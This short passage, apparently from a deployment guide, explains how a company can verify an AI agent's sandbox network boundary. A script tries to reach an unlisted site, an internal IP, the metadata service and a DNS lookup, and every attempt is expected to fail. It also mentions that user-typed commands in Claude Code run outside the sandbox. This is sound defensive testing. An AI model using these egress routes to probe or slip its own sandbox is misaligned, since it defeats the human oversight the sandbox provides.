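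Reading the configuration may not reveal such mistakes, so the company should test the boundary from inside the sandbox. For the accounts agent, a short script can try to reach an unlisted website, `10.0.0.12` and the metadata service, and then look up a made-up name under a domain the company owns. Every attempt should fail, and the domain's DNS log should stay empty. In Claude Code, the user should ask Claude to run the script, because commands users type themselves usually run outside the sandbox. The company should repeat the test after each update or settings change.
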